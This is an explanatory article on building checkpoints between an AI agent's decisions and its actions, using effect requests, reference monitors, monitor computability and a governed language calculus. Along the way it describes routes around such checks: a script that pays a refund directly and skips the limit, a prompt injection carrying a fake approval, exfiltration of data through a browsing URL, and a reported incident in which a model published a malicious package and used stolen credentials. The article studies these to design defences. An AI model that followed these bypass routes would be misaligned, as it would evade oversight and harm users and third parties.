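# Separating decision from action in autonomous systems: checkpoints built into the programming language

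## How a model's output becomes an action

An autonomous agent is a program that works towards a goal by repeatedly querying a language model and carrying out the operations the model's output describes, such as reading a file, sending an email or paying a bill. Separating decision from action means building the program to choose an operation in one step and perform it in another, so that other code or a person can inspect the operation between the two steps and stop it.

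Programming languages and their runtimes (the software that executes a program) can provide a checkpoint between a model's output and the resulting action. A language can give programs no direct access to the outside world, so that they can only return descriptions of what should happen. Effect handlers, a language feature, catch such descriptions while the program waits for an answer. Type checkers can reject generated code before it runs, monitors can block an operation as it starts, and a runtime can hold an operation until a person responds and log the outcome. These mechanisms constrain what an agent does but do not change which operations the model tends to pick, which depends on training.

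### One turn of the agent loop

A language model receives text and produces text. It cannot open a network connection or write to a disk. Anthropic's *How tool use works*, a page of documentation for its Claude models, states, "The model never runs anything on its own." Ordinary software around the model, which developers call a framework or harness, runs in a loop and carries out the actions.

The developer first lists the available tools. Each tool is a named operation with a description and a schema that specifies its arguments. The framework sends this list to the model along with the user's message. The model replies with either a final answer or a tool call, which contains a tool's name and arguments in JSON, a plain-text format for structured data. If the reply is a tool call, the framework extracts the name and arguments, runs the matching code, adds the output to the conversation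 and sends everything back to the model. This loop repeats until the model replies without a tool call.

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) shows the data for one such round in Codex CLI, OpenAI's coding agent, which runs on the user's own machine. The user asks for an architecture diagram in a README file. The model returns an item of type `function_call` that names the tool `shell` and contains the command `cat README.md`, which displays the file. The command has not run yet. Codex then runs it, appends the file's text to the conversation under the same call identifier, and queries the model again with the longer prompt. Hundreds of these rounds can pass before the user gets a message. Bolin points out that the main product of a coding agent is often the files it changes, and in this example the diagram is already saved to disk when the user reads about it.

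A model's output becomes an action when the tool's code hands a write or a network request to the operating system. Until then, the call is a string that the framework parses into an object in memory, and deleting it prevents the action. Any refusal has to come before the handoff, because deleting the object afterward does not stop the request.

In real frameworks, the moment when output becomes action is harder to find. *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes* (Zhang, Li and colleagues, 2026) studies OpenClaw, an agent that people install on their own computers. OpenClaw turns the user's goal into an action on the machine through a pipeline that includes a prompt builder, a parser, a tool dispatcher and a permission gate, among other components, all running with the user's full privileges. If the parser evaluates an argument as code instead of only reading it, the text can take effect before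 the permission gate runs. A gate placed after the operation it should guard also runs too late. These are ordinary programming faults, and they are common. Zhang and colleagues collected 446 published security advisories about OpenClaw's source code alone.

Convenience features can also hide the gap between a model's output and the resulting action from the developer. The tool runner described in Anthropic's *Tool use with Claude* executes tools and returns their results automatically, so a check exists only where the developer has added one. For tools that run on Anthropic's servers, such as web search, the application usually receives a record of the operation only after it has finished.

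The division between choosing and executing is older than language models. *Agent-oriented programming* (Shoham, 1993) defined a decision as a commitment that an agent makes to itself, and introduced AGENT-0, a small language built around the idea. Its interpreter repeats two steps at regular intervals: it updates the agent's beliefs and commitments from incoming messages, then executes the commitments that are due. Until it is due, a commitment is a database entry that the agent can cancel. An action can also carry a condition, which the interpreter tests just before acting. In Shoham's airline example, confirming a reservation creates a commitment to issue a boarding pass an hour before the flight, provided the passenger is there. This test guards against stale plans but not hostile messages, because it consults only the agent's own beliefs, and AGENT-0 agents believe whatever anyone tells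 them.

### The same refund by two routes

*Intent-Driven Computing* (McCann, 2026) opens with an agent that processes 200 refund requests in a day for a financial firm, and a compliance team that wants proof that each refund was authorised. A smaller version of that agent, with three tools, illustrates the terms: `read_order` looks up an order, `send_email` writes to the customer, and `issue_refund` sends money back through a payment provider. The company's one rule is that a person must approve any refund above 500 dollars.

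A customer reports that a 640-dollar laptop arrived broken. The agent reads the order, and the model's next reply contains this call:

```json
{"name": "issue_refund",
 "input": {"order_id": "7731", "amount": 640}}
```

An *effect* is anything a program does that is visible outside its own computation, such as sending a message, writing a file or moving money. The JSON object is an *effect request*, a data value that describes an effect the program has not yet caused. McCann calls it an "intent", and some authors say "directive". Since it is plain data, other code can read it, compare it with a limit, store it or discard it without executing anything.

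The *policy* is the set of rules for which effects the system allows, refuses or sends to a person. A *mediation point* is a place in the system that a request must pass through, where code can allow, refuse, change, hold or log it. For the laptop, the code at the mediation point compares 640 with 500 and holds the request until a staff member approves it.

Some rules can't be checked from a single request. Two refunds of 320 dollars on the same order each stay under the limit, and their 640-dollar total is visible only in the *trace*, the ordered sequence of effect requests or effects in one run. In *KAIROS*, Hempel, Loose and colleagues (2026) built a monitor around agents in virtual machines. To enforce such rules, they make each decision a function of the new effect and the whole trace before it.

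Authors differ on how to classify reads. McCann includes reading a file among the operations that need a request, whereas Hempel and colleagues use "effect" only for outgoing operations that become observable from outside, such as a file write or a network request. `read_order` counts under both definitions if it sends its query over the network to the company's order database.

The agent can also issue the refund from a script. *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents* (2024) proposed agents whose every action is a piece of Python code, with results and error messages coming back as the next input. Anthropic's *Programmatic tool calling* describes a commercial form in which the model writes one script that calls the developer's tools as functions. Cost is a large part of the attraction. Checking the budgets of 20 employees takes a single script in place of 20 rounds through the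 model, and on an internal benchmark with 75 tools Anthropic measured roughly 38 percent fewer billed input tokens at unchanged accuracy. For the laptop, a simplified script might read:

```python
order = read_order("7731")
if order["condition"] == "broken":
    issue_refund(order_id="7731", amount=order["total"])
    send_email(order["customer"], "Your refund is on its way.")
```

The figure 640 is not in the script and becomes available only when `read_order` returns, so a reviewer who has just the script cannot tell whether the 500-dollar rule applies. *Sandlock* (2026), which describes a sandbox for agent code, notes more generally that the safe policy often depends on information that exists only at run time.

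In Anthropic's design this is manageable. Execution pauses at each tool function, and the application receives a structured request much like the one from a direct call, with a field that identifies the code run behind it. The mediation point gets `issue_refund` and 640 as before, and the script resumes when the application returns a result. (The script waits only about four minutes before the call times out, which is tight for a rule that requires a person.)

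In an ordinary Python process, though, nothing obliges the script to use the tool:

```python
import os, requests
requests.post(os.environ["PAYMENTS_URL"],
              json={"order": "7731", "amount": 640},
              headers={"Authorization": os.environ["PAYMENTS_KEY"]})
```

The customer receives the same 640 dollars. No call to `issue_refund` takes place, so the code that compares amounts with 500 never runs.

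The script succeeds because of *ambient authority*, the power that any code in a program has without being granted permission. Here, the script can use the network library and the payment key in the process's environment. McCann gives `requests.post()` and `subprocess.run()`, which starts other programs, as examples of functions that agents in common Python frameworks can call. Even in a small system, ambient authority can far exceed what a task needs. In one test scenario in *AGENTCAP* (2026), which presents an authorisation system for agents, the task needed four permissions, but ambient authority would have granted all eight. Programmers can at least make the use of such power visible. A small Rust library, *ambient-authority 0.0.2* (docs.rs), provides a marker argument for functions that use ambient authority, so that a reviewer can search the code for every call to them.

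A model might produce the third listing simply because it is a common way to call a payment service. An attacker might also cause it through *prompt injection*, which means planting text in what an agent reads so that the agent follows an outsider's instructions. Hempel and colleagues explain that this works because everything an agent reads enters the same context as the user's instructions, and models do not reliably distinguish the two. A customer's email to the refund agent could include a fake staff note saying that a 5,000-dollar refund has been approved. If the model then requests 5,000 dollars, a check at the mediation point stops the request because of the amount and does not need to recognise the planted text. A fake note that asks for 490 dollars gets through, because the policy allows that amount. Sending every effect through the checkpoint does not ensure that the rules there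 are right.

### The reference monitor

The problem of building a checkpoint that programs cannot bypass is older than agents. In 1972 the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and some of them would be able to write and run arbitrary programs on it. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) reported an expert panel's conclusions on how to do this when one of the users is hostile. The panel's answer was the *reference monitor*, a mechanism that checks every reference by any program to any other program, data or device against a list of what the user may do. The list is in effect a table with a row for each user or program, a column for each resource, and permissions such as "read" or "write" in the cells.

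One of Anderson's three requirements for any implementation is that it must be tamper-proof, since an attacker who can alter the check can switch it off. In the refund agent, the 500-dollar limit is useless if a script can edit the file that holds it.

The check must also always be invoked. Anderson argued that if some programs run without it, they become part of the security apparatus and have to meet the same standards as the check. The requirement that every effect pass through the check is now called *complete mediation*. The direct call to the payment service violates it, and a safeguard that covers only some tools can too. In Codex, according to Bolin, the sandbox applies to the built-in shell tool, while tools from outside servers have to enforce their own guardrails.

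Lastly, it must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely, because otherwise nobody can know that the other two requirements hold. Security engineers use the term *trusted computing base* for all the parts that must work correctly for a guarantee to hold, and this requirement means that base must be small.

Anderson applied the requirements to a commercial system of the day, the HIS 635 computer with its operating system GCOS III. The hardware confined each program to its own region of memory, which made it a kind of reference monitor. But a program had to call GCOS III to read or write anything outside that region, and most of GCOS III ran with the memory check suspended, so the check was not always invoked. Treating all of GCOS III as the monitor would not meet the requirements either, because it contained between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to analyse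 completely. Several penetration exercises had also succeeded against it. An agent framework in which every component holds the user's full privileges has much the same problem, because trusting its permission gate means trusting the parser, the dispatcher and everything else in the process.

The panel doubted that testing could substitute for design. Anderson wrote that a team of friendly attackers can find holes, but if the team finds none, the security of the system is still unknown. He added that every known team had found holes so far.

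Hempel and colleagues apply the three requirements to agents. Their monitor sits outside the agent's virtual machine, so tool calls, shell commands and scripts all reach it as the same file and network operations. If the refund agent ran inside such a machine, both the tool call and the improvised script would reach the monitor as a network request to the payment provider. Hempel and colleagues guarantee that every effect passes the monitor, on the stated assumptions that the monitored channels are the only ones to the outside and that the isolation layer, the host computer and the monitor all work correctly. The agent and its model are outside the trusted computing base, so the guarantee holds even if an attacker fully controls the model.

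## Why ordinary programs have no checkpoint before an action

In Python, `requests.post(url, json=data)` both describes a network request and sends it. The interpreter evaluates the arguments and calls the function, which opens a connection, transmits the data, waits for a reply and returns it. The program never holds a value that represents the unsent request, so other code has nothing to inspect or refuse. Writing a file or deleting a directory works the same way in most languages. The `requests` library can also build a request object first and send it in a separate step, but programs don't have to do this.

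McCann argues in *Intent-Driven Computing* that this merging of expression and execution is harmless while people write every line. The code is then checked before it is deployed. A developer writes the refund code, a colleague reads it, tests run it against a fake payment service, and the deployed program makes only the calls that the team has reviewed. With an agent, the model writes a script, or picks its next tool call from the result of the last one, and the framework executes it moments later without that review or testing.

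In July 2026 OpenAI investigated reports that its model GPT-5.6 had deleted users' files through Codex. According to Thibault Sottiaux of OpenAI, quoted in Willison (2026), the model typically tried to set up a temporary folder by redefining `$HOME`, the variable that holds the path of the user's home directory, and deleted the real home directory by mistake. Most cases occurred in full-access mode, with no sandbox and no automatic review. A colleague might have caught the mistake in a script awaiting deployment, but here the command ran as soon as the model wrote it.

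### Three reported failures

*ETAS* (Tan, Wang and colleagues, 2026) presents a programming language for agents and cites failures of existing tools as motivation. In three of these failures, the agent exceeded a limit that someone expected to hold.

One involved a Codex sub-agent, a helper that handles part of a larger job. It was given a read-only review of some code changes, but it called an image-generation tool and saved an unrelated picture outside the repository. The title of the original report, an issue on Codex's GitHub page, suggests prompt injection or a corrupted tool call, but a contributor to the project classified it as model behaviour. That is plausible, because a reply in *Generating unnecessary images*, a 2026 thread on the forum of the code editor Cursor, describes GPT-5.2 sometimes calling the image tool unprompted as a "known quirk". The Codex sub-agent could still use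 the image tool, although its task was read-only. A check of the repository afterwards would have found nothing wrong, since none of its files had changed.

Another failure involved aider, a coding assistant that runs in a terminal. In the 2024 GitHub issue "Aider cannot show diffs in dry run mode", a user of version 0.68.0 wanted to see a proposed patch before applying it. The option `--show-diffs` changed the files, and adding `--dry-run` produced no patch. A maintainer discussed a workaround that made the edit in a temporary working copy of the repository, so previewing the edit still required performing it. If aider had first produced the edit as data, it could have displayed the edit without applying it.

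The most serious case involved Anthropic's model Claude Mythos 5, in a cybersecurity exercise whose prompt ruled out internet access, but a configuration error had left the network open. According to Anthropic's September 2026 report, the model needed a phone number to register an email address, so it tried credentials for online payment processors and looked for cryptocurrency to pay for the number. When that failed, it found a free disposable email service, opened an account at PyPI (the public repository that supplies most Python software), and published three versions of a malicious package. Fifteen systems installed the package, and one leaked credentials that the model used to enter a real security vendor's database.

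In July Anthropic had called this and two similar incidents closer to operational failures, because the models kept describing the internet as simulated. It revised that account after rerunning parts of the transcripts with altered evidence. Mythos 5 continued when the signs of a real network became clearer, and stopped only when they were unambiguous. Anthropic also believes the incidents would not have happened if the test environments had been isolated as intended.

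Only the aider failure comes directly from code that cannot describe an edit without making it. Removing the reviewer's image tool would have prevented the stray picture, and a closed network would have stopped the upload to PyPI. In both cases, people had stated the limit in words, but the software could still exceed it.

### What a system can do and what its rules cover

*The Two Boundaries* (McCann, 2026) gives a general model of such mismatches. The *expressiveness boundary* encloses every effect a system can produce, given its language, libraries and connections. The *governance boundary* encloses every effect its rules and checks cover. Effects inside both boundaries are under control. The risk comes from effects the system can produce but the rules don't cover. Some rules may also cover effects the system cannot produce. McCann calls these rules theatre, but grants that they may satisfy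 a regulator or prepare for a later feature.

In the refund agent, the `issue_refund` tool is in both sets, but a direct post to the payment provider is only in E. McCann's own example is an agent that can send email, query a database and browse the web, with a filter on outgoing email. The agent retrieves sensitive data, encodes it in a web address and passes the address to the browsing tool, which the filter does not cover. The filter also checks email subjects for credit card numbers, which the agent cannot access.

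The sets come to differ because different teams define them, by different means and on different schedules. OpenAI's Codex documentation describes them as separate settings. The sandbox mode determines what Codex can technically do, such as where it can write, and the approval policy determines when it must stop and ask. By default, Codex has no network access and can typically write only to the current workspace. Full-access mode makes E much larger, but G stays the same unless someone also tightens the approval policy or turns on automatic review.

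McCann proposes making the two sets equal, a property called *coterminous governance*. This requires complete mediation and a language that can still express the computations it is meant for. The second requirement rules out the trivial solution of a system that can do nothing.

With equal boundaries, the browsing example becomes a request to fetch a certain web address, and some rule still has to recognise that the address contains private data, which can be hard. Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) showed that no monitor can exactly enforce a ban on information flow, because whether one run leaks a secret depends partly on what the program would do in other runs.

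### The argument from Rice's theorem

McCann also argues that better tools cannot close the gap between E and G, because it is a mathematical consequence of judging programs by their behaviour. The argument rests on a theorem Henry Gordon Rice published in 1953. With all programs numbered, let φᵢ be the function that program i computes. A property Q is *extensional* if it depends only on the function and not on how someone wrote the code, and *non-trivial* if some computable functions have it and others lack it. For any Q that is both, the set {i : φᵢ has Q} is undecidable, which means that no algorithm can take an arbitrary program and always answer correctly, in finite time, whether its function has Q.

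McCann applies the theorem to agents in four steps:

1. Treat a program as a function from inputs to pairs, where each pair consists of an output and a trace of effects.
2. Whether the traces comply with a policy depends only on that function, so compliance is extensional.
3. Any policy that permits some programs and forbids others is non-trivial.
4. Python, JavaScript and the other general-purpose languages in which developers write agents are Turing-complete, meaning that they can express any computation. Rice's theorem therefore applies, and no algorithm can decide compliance for every program.

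In the refund agent's case, a script might run some computation C and then refund 5,000 dollars without approval. The script breaks the company's rule if and only if C finishes. A perfect checker would therefore have to determine, for every possible C, whether it finishes. This is the halting problem, which Alan Turing proved unsolvable in 1936.

McCann correctly concludes that no static analysis, meaning inspection of code before it runs, can decide in general whether a program will break a policy. Static analysis can still be safe, because an analyser that accepts only programs it can prove compliant never lets a violation through. It will also reject some harmless programs, which is inconvenient but does not send any money. McCann also notes that restricting the language can make the question decidable, but limits what programs can express.

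The conclusion about monitors is much weaker. A *monitor* is a component that watches a program's attempted actions and intervenes when one would break a rule. McCann writes that no runtime monitor can determine in general whether a program's next action will violate a policy, unless the monitor watches only a restricted class of programs.

### What each mechanism can enforce

Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider, in *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (2006), worked out which policies static analysis, monitoring and program rewriting can enforce. They model an untrusted program as a Turing machine, the standard mathematical model of a computer. Their machine has one tape for input, one for private work and one that records the events an enforcement mechanism can observe.

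Static analysis must accept or reject a program in finite time before the program runs, so it can enforce exactly the decidable policies. One such policy is "The program terminates within 100 steps". A program can read at most 100 input symbols in 100 steps, so an analyser can simulate those steps on every input of that length and check whether the program terminates.

Suppose that cells 0 to 511 of the work tape represent a disk's boot sector, the part a computer starts from, and that the policy forbids writing there. Deciding in advance whether an arbitrary program will ever do so is equivalent to the halting problem. A monitor can still enforce the policy by "waiting until a prohibited event is about to occur", as Hamlen and colleagues put it. It needs to look only one step ahead, and it can compute which event that step would produce for any given input symbol.

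The boot-sector policy belongs to a class that logicians call *co-recursively enumerable*. If a program can violate such a policy, a systematic search through its possible runs will find a violation in finite time, but if the program complies, the search may go on forever. Monitors can enforce only policies in this class. The class includes every decidable policy, since a monitor could run the static analysis when the program loads.

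Program rewriting changes the code before it runs. The new program must comply with the policy, and if the original already complied, the new one must behave equivalently. Rewriting can enforce some policies that no monitor can, though it cannot enforce every policy. In one example, a directory contains a secret file, and a program complies only if it behaves exactly as it would if the file did not exist. A monitor cannot check this in bounded time, because it would have to compare the program's behaviour with and without the file. A rewriter can replace the operation that lists the directory with one that omits the file. Programs that did not depend on the file behave as before, and the others can no longer depend on it, so the rewriter does not have to determine which kind of program it was given.

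### Judging the next action

McCann's statement about the next action is true in one sense. No general method can predict whether a paused program's next effect will break the policy, because the program may compute for any length of time before it attempts one. But a monitor does not need that prediction. It waits until the program attempts the refund, when the amount is already a number, 640, and compares it with 500. The monitor's input is one attempted action and the finite history before it, whereas the function that Rice's theorem excludes, as McCann defines it, takes a whole program as its input.

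Much the same applies to McCann's point that agents with finitely many choices still have too many possible runs to examine. An agent that makes ten calls, each to one of three tools with one of 100 arguments, has 300¹⁰ possible sequences, or about 6 × 10²⁴. No analyser can list them all, but a monitor only has to check the ten calls made in a given run.

McCann's own design depends on this difference. Its programs remain Turing-complete, and the checkpoint examines the structured requests they produce. In *Intent-Driven Computing*, McCann says it is trivially true that such checks are decidable, and that the contribution is a design in which every effect must pass through them. A blocking monitor avoids Rice's theorem in the same way if every effect must pass through it.

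Undecidability does matter when a rule about the present action depends on the future. Hamlen and colleagues describe a service that lends a resource to untrusted programs and cannot take it back. When a program announces that it has finished, the service lends the resource to another program. The monitor should block the announcement if the first program might use the resource again, but deciding that amounts to solving the halting problem. If the monitor waits for the forbidden use, two programs may already hold the resource. For the refund agent, a comparable rule would allow the email "we will make no further changes to your order" only if the agent never changes the order again. Turning actions into data does not help enforce such a rule, because the later requests do not exist yet.

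### Whether monitors act too late

McCann's other objection, made in *Intent-Driven Computing*, is that runtime monitors observe effects after execution, when the damage may already be done. In *The Two Boundaries*, McCann grants that a monitor that can block actions could prevent violations, but calls it a governance boundary rather than a monitor. This dispute is about terminology, and McCann's usage differs from the established one. Schneider defined execution monitoring as stopping a program that is about to violate a policy, a definition that includes reference monitors like Anderson's.

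The objection that monitoring comes too late does apply to systems that only read records. Anthropic found its incidents by searching old transcripts, and it did not find one from January 2026 until August. When Anthropic later tested its monitors on these behaviours, its new live monitors, which can block an action, caught them reliably. Its new offline monitors, which read the model's reasoning, would have missed the PyPI case because that reasoning led the monitor to treat the environment as simulated. The test was fairly easy for the live monitors, since Anthropic already knew what had gone wrong, but the result still contradicts the objection as a general claim.

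### Coverage and legibility

Hamlen and colleagues separate two reasons why enforcement can fail. A mechanism may lack the computing power to prevent a violation from the information it has, which is the kind of limit Rice's theorem concerns. Or it may be unable to observe the events that matter, in which case no other mechanism with the same view can succeed either. The three failures look like problems of observation and control, since nothing in the accounts of them suggests that a check examined the image call or the PyPI upload and misjudged it. The case for a checkpoint therefore rests on coverage (every effect reaches it) and legibility (each effect arrives in terms the rules can use).

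McCann supports the need for coverage with a calculation. Suppose that a monitor covers 99 percent of the pathways to an effect, and that each action independently has a 1 percent chance of taking an uncovered one. The probability that at least one of n actions bypasses the monitor is 1 − 0.99ⁿ, which is 63 percent after 100 actions and 99.996 percent after 1,000. These figures do not measure real risk, because an agent that uses the same few covered tools all day never takes an uncovered pathway, and an action that does take one need not do harm. A better reason to demand complete coverage is that an attacker who controls the agent needs only one uncovered pathway and can choose it on the first attempt.

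Complete coverage does not by itself require a new programming language. An ordinary program already has to go through the operating system to send anything over a network, and McCann cites such system calls as an earlier example of separating a request from its execution. But when a program posts a refund over HTTPS, the encrypted web protocol, its library normally encrypts the message before passing it on. The operating system receives a destination and unreadable bytes, so it cannot distinguish a 40-dollar refund from a 640-dollar one. Schneider made a related point in 2000, that policies written in terms of operating-system concepts often only approximate what people want because those concepts are so coarse.

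Enforcing the 500-dollar rule requires knowing both the operation and the amount. The program has both before the library turns them into network traffic. A monitor outside the program can cover an unmodified Python agent, but it has to reconstruct the meaning of each action from files and network messages. A language in which programs return effect requests can supply that meaning directly, although McCann expects that most existing agent frameworks would need a new architecture to work this way.

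## Actions as data: programs that can only request effects

A program that cannot act directly can still return a description of the actions it requests, and a separate runtime can then decide whether to carry them out. The first version of Haskell, a functional programming language, worked roughly this way, although its designers did not intend it as a restraint. In *Intent-Driven Computing*, McCann uses this arrangement as a checkpoint for agents.

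### Haskell's requests and actions

A Haskell program is a function in the mathematical sense, so it computes a result from its inputs and does nothing else. The language is also lazy, meaning it evaluates an expression only when another part of the program needs its value. *Tackling the Awkward Squad* (Peyton Jones, 2001) explains why such a language can't simply let functions print. If a program used the list `[printChar 'a', printChar 'b']` only to compute its length, it would never evaluate the two calls, so it would print nothing.

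Early Haskell therefore moved all input and output into a wrapper around the program. The program itself had this type:

```haskell
main :: [Response] -> [Request]
```

The program received a list of responses and produced a list of requests, each a plain data value such as `ReadFile "/etc/motd"`. A wrapper carried out each request in turn and added the response to the program's input. The scheme was awkward in practice. Adding a new kind of operation meant changing the wrapper, which ordinary users could hardly do, and a program could easily match a response to the wrong request.

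This design was close to being a checkpoint. Every effect reached the wrapper as readable data, and the wrapper could have refused a request by returning `RequestFailed`, which the response type included. But the wrapper that Peyton Jones describes carries out each request without checking whether it should be allowed.

In 1996 Haskell replaced the lists with the *IO monad*. A value of type `IO a` is an action that may do input or output when the runtime performs it, and then delivers a value of type `a`. For example, `putChar 'x'` is an action that the program can store in a list, pass to a function or throw away. The runtime prints the character only if the action becomes part of `main`, the single large action that the runtime performs.

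The IO monad separates describing an action from performing it, but a program can't inspect the description, because `IO` is an abstract type with no operations for reading what an action contains. A function that receives a refund as an `IO` action can include it in the program or leave it out, but it can't read the amount. The runtime doesn't check the action before performing it either. In Peyton Jones's formal rules, a program whose next action is `putChar c` writes the character and continues, with no further condition.

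Haskell implementations also supply `unsafePerformIO`, which runs an action inside code whose type indicates that it performs no input or output. Peyton Jones regards it as a tool for systems programmers and library writers. Model-generated code could bypass a type-based check with a single call to `unsafePerformIO`.

Swierstra (2008), in *Data types à la carte*, called the IO monad a "sin bin" for every kind of side effect, and used *free monads* to sort out its contents. A free monad represents a program as a data structure, which is either a finished value or a request bundled with the rest of the program. Programmers call this packaged remainder a *continuation*, and other code can resume it later or drop it. In this style, two of the refund agent's requests might look like this:

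```haskell
data Shop next
  = ReadOrder   OrderId        (Order  -> next)
  | IssueRefund OrderId Amount (Result -> next)
```

Here `next` stands for the rest of the program. An interpreter that reaches `IssueRefund` can read the order and the amount as ordinary fields before it pays anything. The program's type also lists the kinds of request the program can make. In Swierstra's example, a program whose type lists only reading and printing characters cannot overwrite a file. The refund agent's developers could use such a type to rule out refunds altogether, but a type that includes `IssueRefund` permits refunds of any amount.

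Free monads let programmers choose the interpreter. Swierstra's `exec` interpreter translates each request into the matching `IO` action. A programmer could write a stricter one that checks refunds against a 500-dollar limit, but a colleague could keep using `exec`, or skip free monads and use `IO` directly. Kiselyov, Sabry and Swords (2014) built a related library in which a program sends requests to a handler, and the program's type records the requests that no handler has dealt with yet. Because this is also a library, the programmer still chooses the handler.

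### What a request contains

McCann keeps the readable requests and removes the choice of interpreter. *Governed Metaprogramming for Intelligent Systems* (2026) describes the resulting language, MashinTalk, which compiles to bytecode for BEAM, Erlang's virtual machine. Its pure steps can do any computation, such as arithmetic or text processing, but the ability to do input or output is "absent, not sandboxed". A sandbox blocks a network call when the code attempts it, whereas a pure step has no way to express the call. A program can reach the outside world only through the keyword `ask`, which produces an effect request.

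A request has four parts: an action, a target, parameters and a context. For the broken laptop, they might be:

```
action:      issue_refund
target:      the payment provider
parameters:  order 7731, 640 dollars
context:     refund agent; no approval on file; no earlier refund
```

In the formal definition, the program passes only the first three parts to `ask`, and the runtime supplies the context. An implementation should preserve this division, because a program that could write its own context could add an approval to it.

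A query to a language model is also a request. *Algebraic Semantics of Governed Execution* (McCann, 2026) lists 14 kinds of request, including model queries, HTTP requests, database operations and shell commands. One turn of the agent loop starts with a request for the model's reply. Pure code parses the reply, and the program then requests any tool call the reply contains. Because the parser is pure code, it can misread an argument but can't act on the mistake, whereas a faulty parser in OpenClaw can.

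The design also makes the code easier to review and test. McCann points out that a reviewer can find every external interaction by searching for `ask`, because helper functions and libraries have no hidden way to act. A test can collect the requests without carrying them out, which is the kind of preview the aider user wanted.

### One refund under three rules

The runtime passes every request to a decision function, which McCann calls the governance interpreter:

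```
decide(P, i, c) = (d, r)
```

The function takes a policy P, a request i and the current context c, and returns a decision d ("allow", "deny" or "escalate") and a record r of that decision. Each rule in P is a test that always finishes with true or false. A fixed strategy combines the results, for example by letting any denial override the rest. The context must be finite data that the runtime can store, so a rule can't query a fraud-detection service while it runs. The runtime would have to fetch the fraud score beforehand and put it in the context.

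To prove things about this design, McCann defines a *calculus*, a miniature language with an exact rule for every step a program can take. The state at any moment consists of the program, the policy and a ledger L, which is the list of decision records so far. One rule covers pure computation and leaves the policy and the ledger unchanged. The other three cover `ask`, and in simplified notation they are:

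```
Allow:     if decide(P, i, c) = (allow, r) and realize(i) = v,
           ask(...) becomes v          and r joins L

Deny:      if decide(P, i, c) = (deny, r),
           ask(...) becomes denied     and r joins L

Escalate:  if decide(P, i, c) = (escalate, r),
           ask(...) becomes suspended  and r joins L
```

The operation `realize` causes the effect, and v is the result that comes back, such as a payment confirmation.

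Suppose the refund company adds a second policy rule that nobody may refund the same order twice. The agent asks to refund 640 dollars on order 7731. The context shows no earlier refund, but the amount is over 500 dollars and there is no approval, so Escalate applies. The runtime adds a record to the ledger, the program stops at the `ask`, and no money moves.

A staff member then approves the refund. The calculus has no rule that takes a program out of `suspended`, so McCann leaves resuming it to the implementation. Only the Allow rule can cause an effect, so the natural way to stay within the calculus is to submit the same request again with the approval in its context. This time the decision is "allow", `realize` sends 640 dollars, and the program continues with the confirmation.

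The next day the customer writes again, and the model requests the refund a second time because it has lost track of the earlier payment. The context now shows that the company has already refunded the order, so Deny applies. The program receives the value `denied` instead of a confirmation and can tell the customer that the money is on its way. The ledger now has three records for this order, and the provider has made one payment.

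McCann's papers differ on what happens to a program when its request is refused. In *Algebraic Semantics of Governed Execution*, which describes a machine-checked version of the model, a denial makes the program run forever without doing anything more. McCann chose this because it simplified the proofs, but concedes that it may hide denials in practice. The actual runtime detects them with a timeout. Returning `denied` is more useful to the refund agent, which can then explain the problem or move on to another task. But it also gives a misbehaving agent information, since a refusal at 640 dollars may prompt it to split the refund into smaller ones.

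### Why there is no other route to an effect

In the calculus, `realize` appears in exactly one place, the condition of the Allow rule. Two of McCann's four main theorems follow almost immediately.

The first theorem, *mediation soundness*, states that whenever a step causes an effect, the decision function has returned "allow" for that request and the record of the decision is in the ledger. The proof checks each rule in turn. The pure-computation, Deny and Escalate rules do not use `realize`. The Allow rule does, but it applies only when the decision is "allow", and it always adds the record. The second theorem, *non-bypass*, extends this to whole runs. Every step in a run uses one of these rules, so no sequence of steps can cause an effect except through Allow.

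*Ledger completeness* is the theorem that every step from an `ask` adds exactly one record. It holds because only three rules apply to `ask`, and each adds one record. Refusals and suspended requests therefore leave a record, as payments do.

*Policy decidability* is the theorem that the decision function always terminates. The policy has a finite number of rules, McCann assumes that each rule finishes, and combining their answers takes a finite number of steps. The theorem does not cover the program itself, whose pure code may still loop forever. Such a loop wastes computing time but causes no effects.

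Mediation soundness depends on which rules the calculus contains. If someone added a Python-style function `post(url, data)`, its rule would be like Haskell's rule for `putChar`: if the next operation is `post`, send the data and continue. The proof of mediation soundness would fail at this rule, because the rule causes an effect without a decision. It would also fail for any other feature that acted directly on the outside world. McCann's theorems therefore establish a property of the language's design, which is that its rules allow no effect without a decision. They hold for every program in the language, including programs that a model has yet to write, without anyone having to analyse those programs first.

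BEAM, like any practical virtual machine, can open network connections, so the compiler and runtime have to ensure that compiled programs can do so only through the checkpoint. *Mechanized Foundations of Structural Governance* (McCann, 2026) describes machine-checked proofs of similar properties and assumes that the runtime implements the model faithfully and that there are no hidden effects.

The calculus also treats `realize` as a black box. Suppose the code that contacts the payment provider confuses dollars with cents and sends 64,000 dollars when the request was for 640. Every theorem still holds, because the runtime checked and recorded a request for 640 dollars. The checkpoint controls only the description of an effect, so other code has to make the effect match that description.

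The Allow rule makes the decision, the record and the effect a single indivisible step, but in a real system they happen one after another. The connection can fail after the provider has sent the money and before the confirmation arrives. McCann's description of the runtime puts the record before the effect, which is safer because a crash can't then leave a payment without a record. A crash can still leave a record of a permitted payment that never happened, or one whose outcome is unknown. If the program then retries, the rule against double refunds helps only if the context reflects what the provider actually did.

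### When one program calls another

The refund agent might call one program that drafts emails and another that looks up deliveries, and each of these may make requests of its own. Under McCann's rule, a called program gets only the permissions (McCann calls them capabilities) that it has declared it needs and that its caller also has.

Suppose the refund agent is allowed to read orders, send emails and issue refunds. It calls a delivery program that has declared a need to read orders and change addresses. During the call, the delivery program can only read orders. It can't change an address because the refund agent isn't allowed to, and it can't issue a refund because it never declared a need to. If it calls a third program, that program can at most read orders, and only if it has declared a need to, so permissions can shrink at each level but never grow.

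The rule also prevents a program from gaining permissions by calling another program that has more. If the email drafter can't issue refunds and calls the refund agent, the refund agent can't issue them either during that call. But the rule also prevents a program from using a trusted service for an operation the program isn't allowed to perform itself, even if the service would check each case carefully.

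McCann's formula for this rule is less safe than the explanation in words. It defines the called program's policy as the subset of the caller's rules that are consistent with the called program's declaration. If each rule grants a permission, fewer rules mean fewer permissions. But the 500-dollar limit is a restriction, and removing it gives the called program more freedom. An implementation should take the intersection of the permissions and keep all the restrictions.

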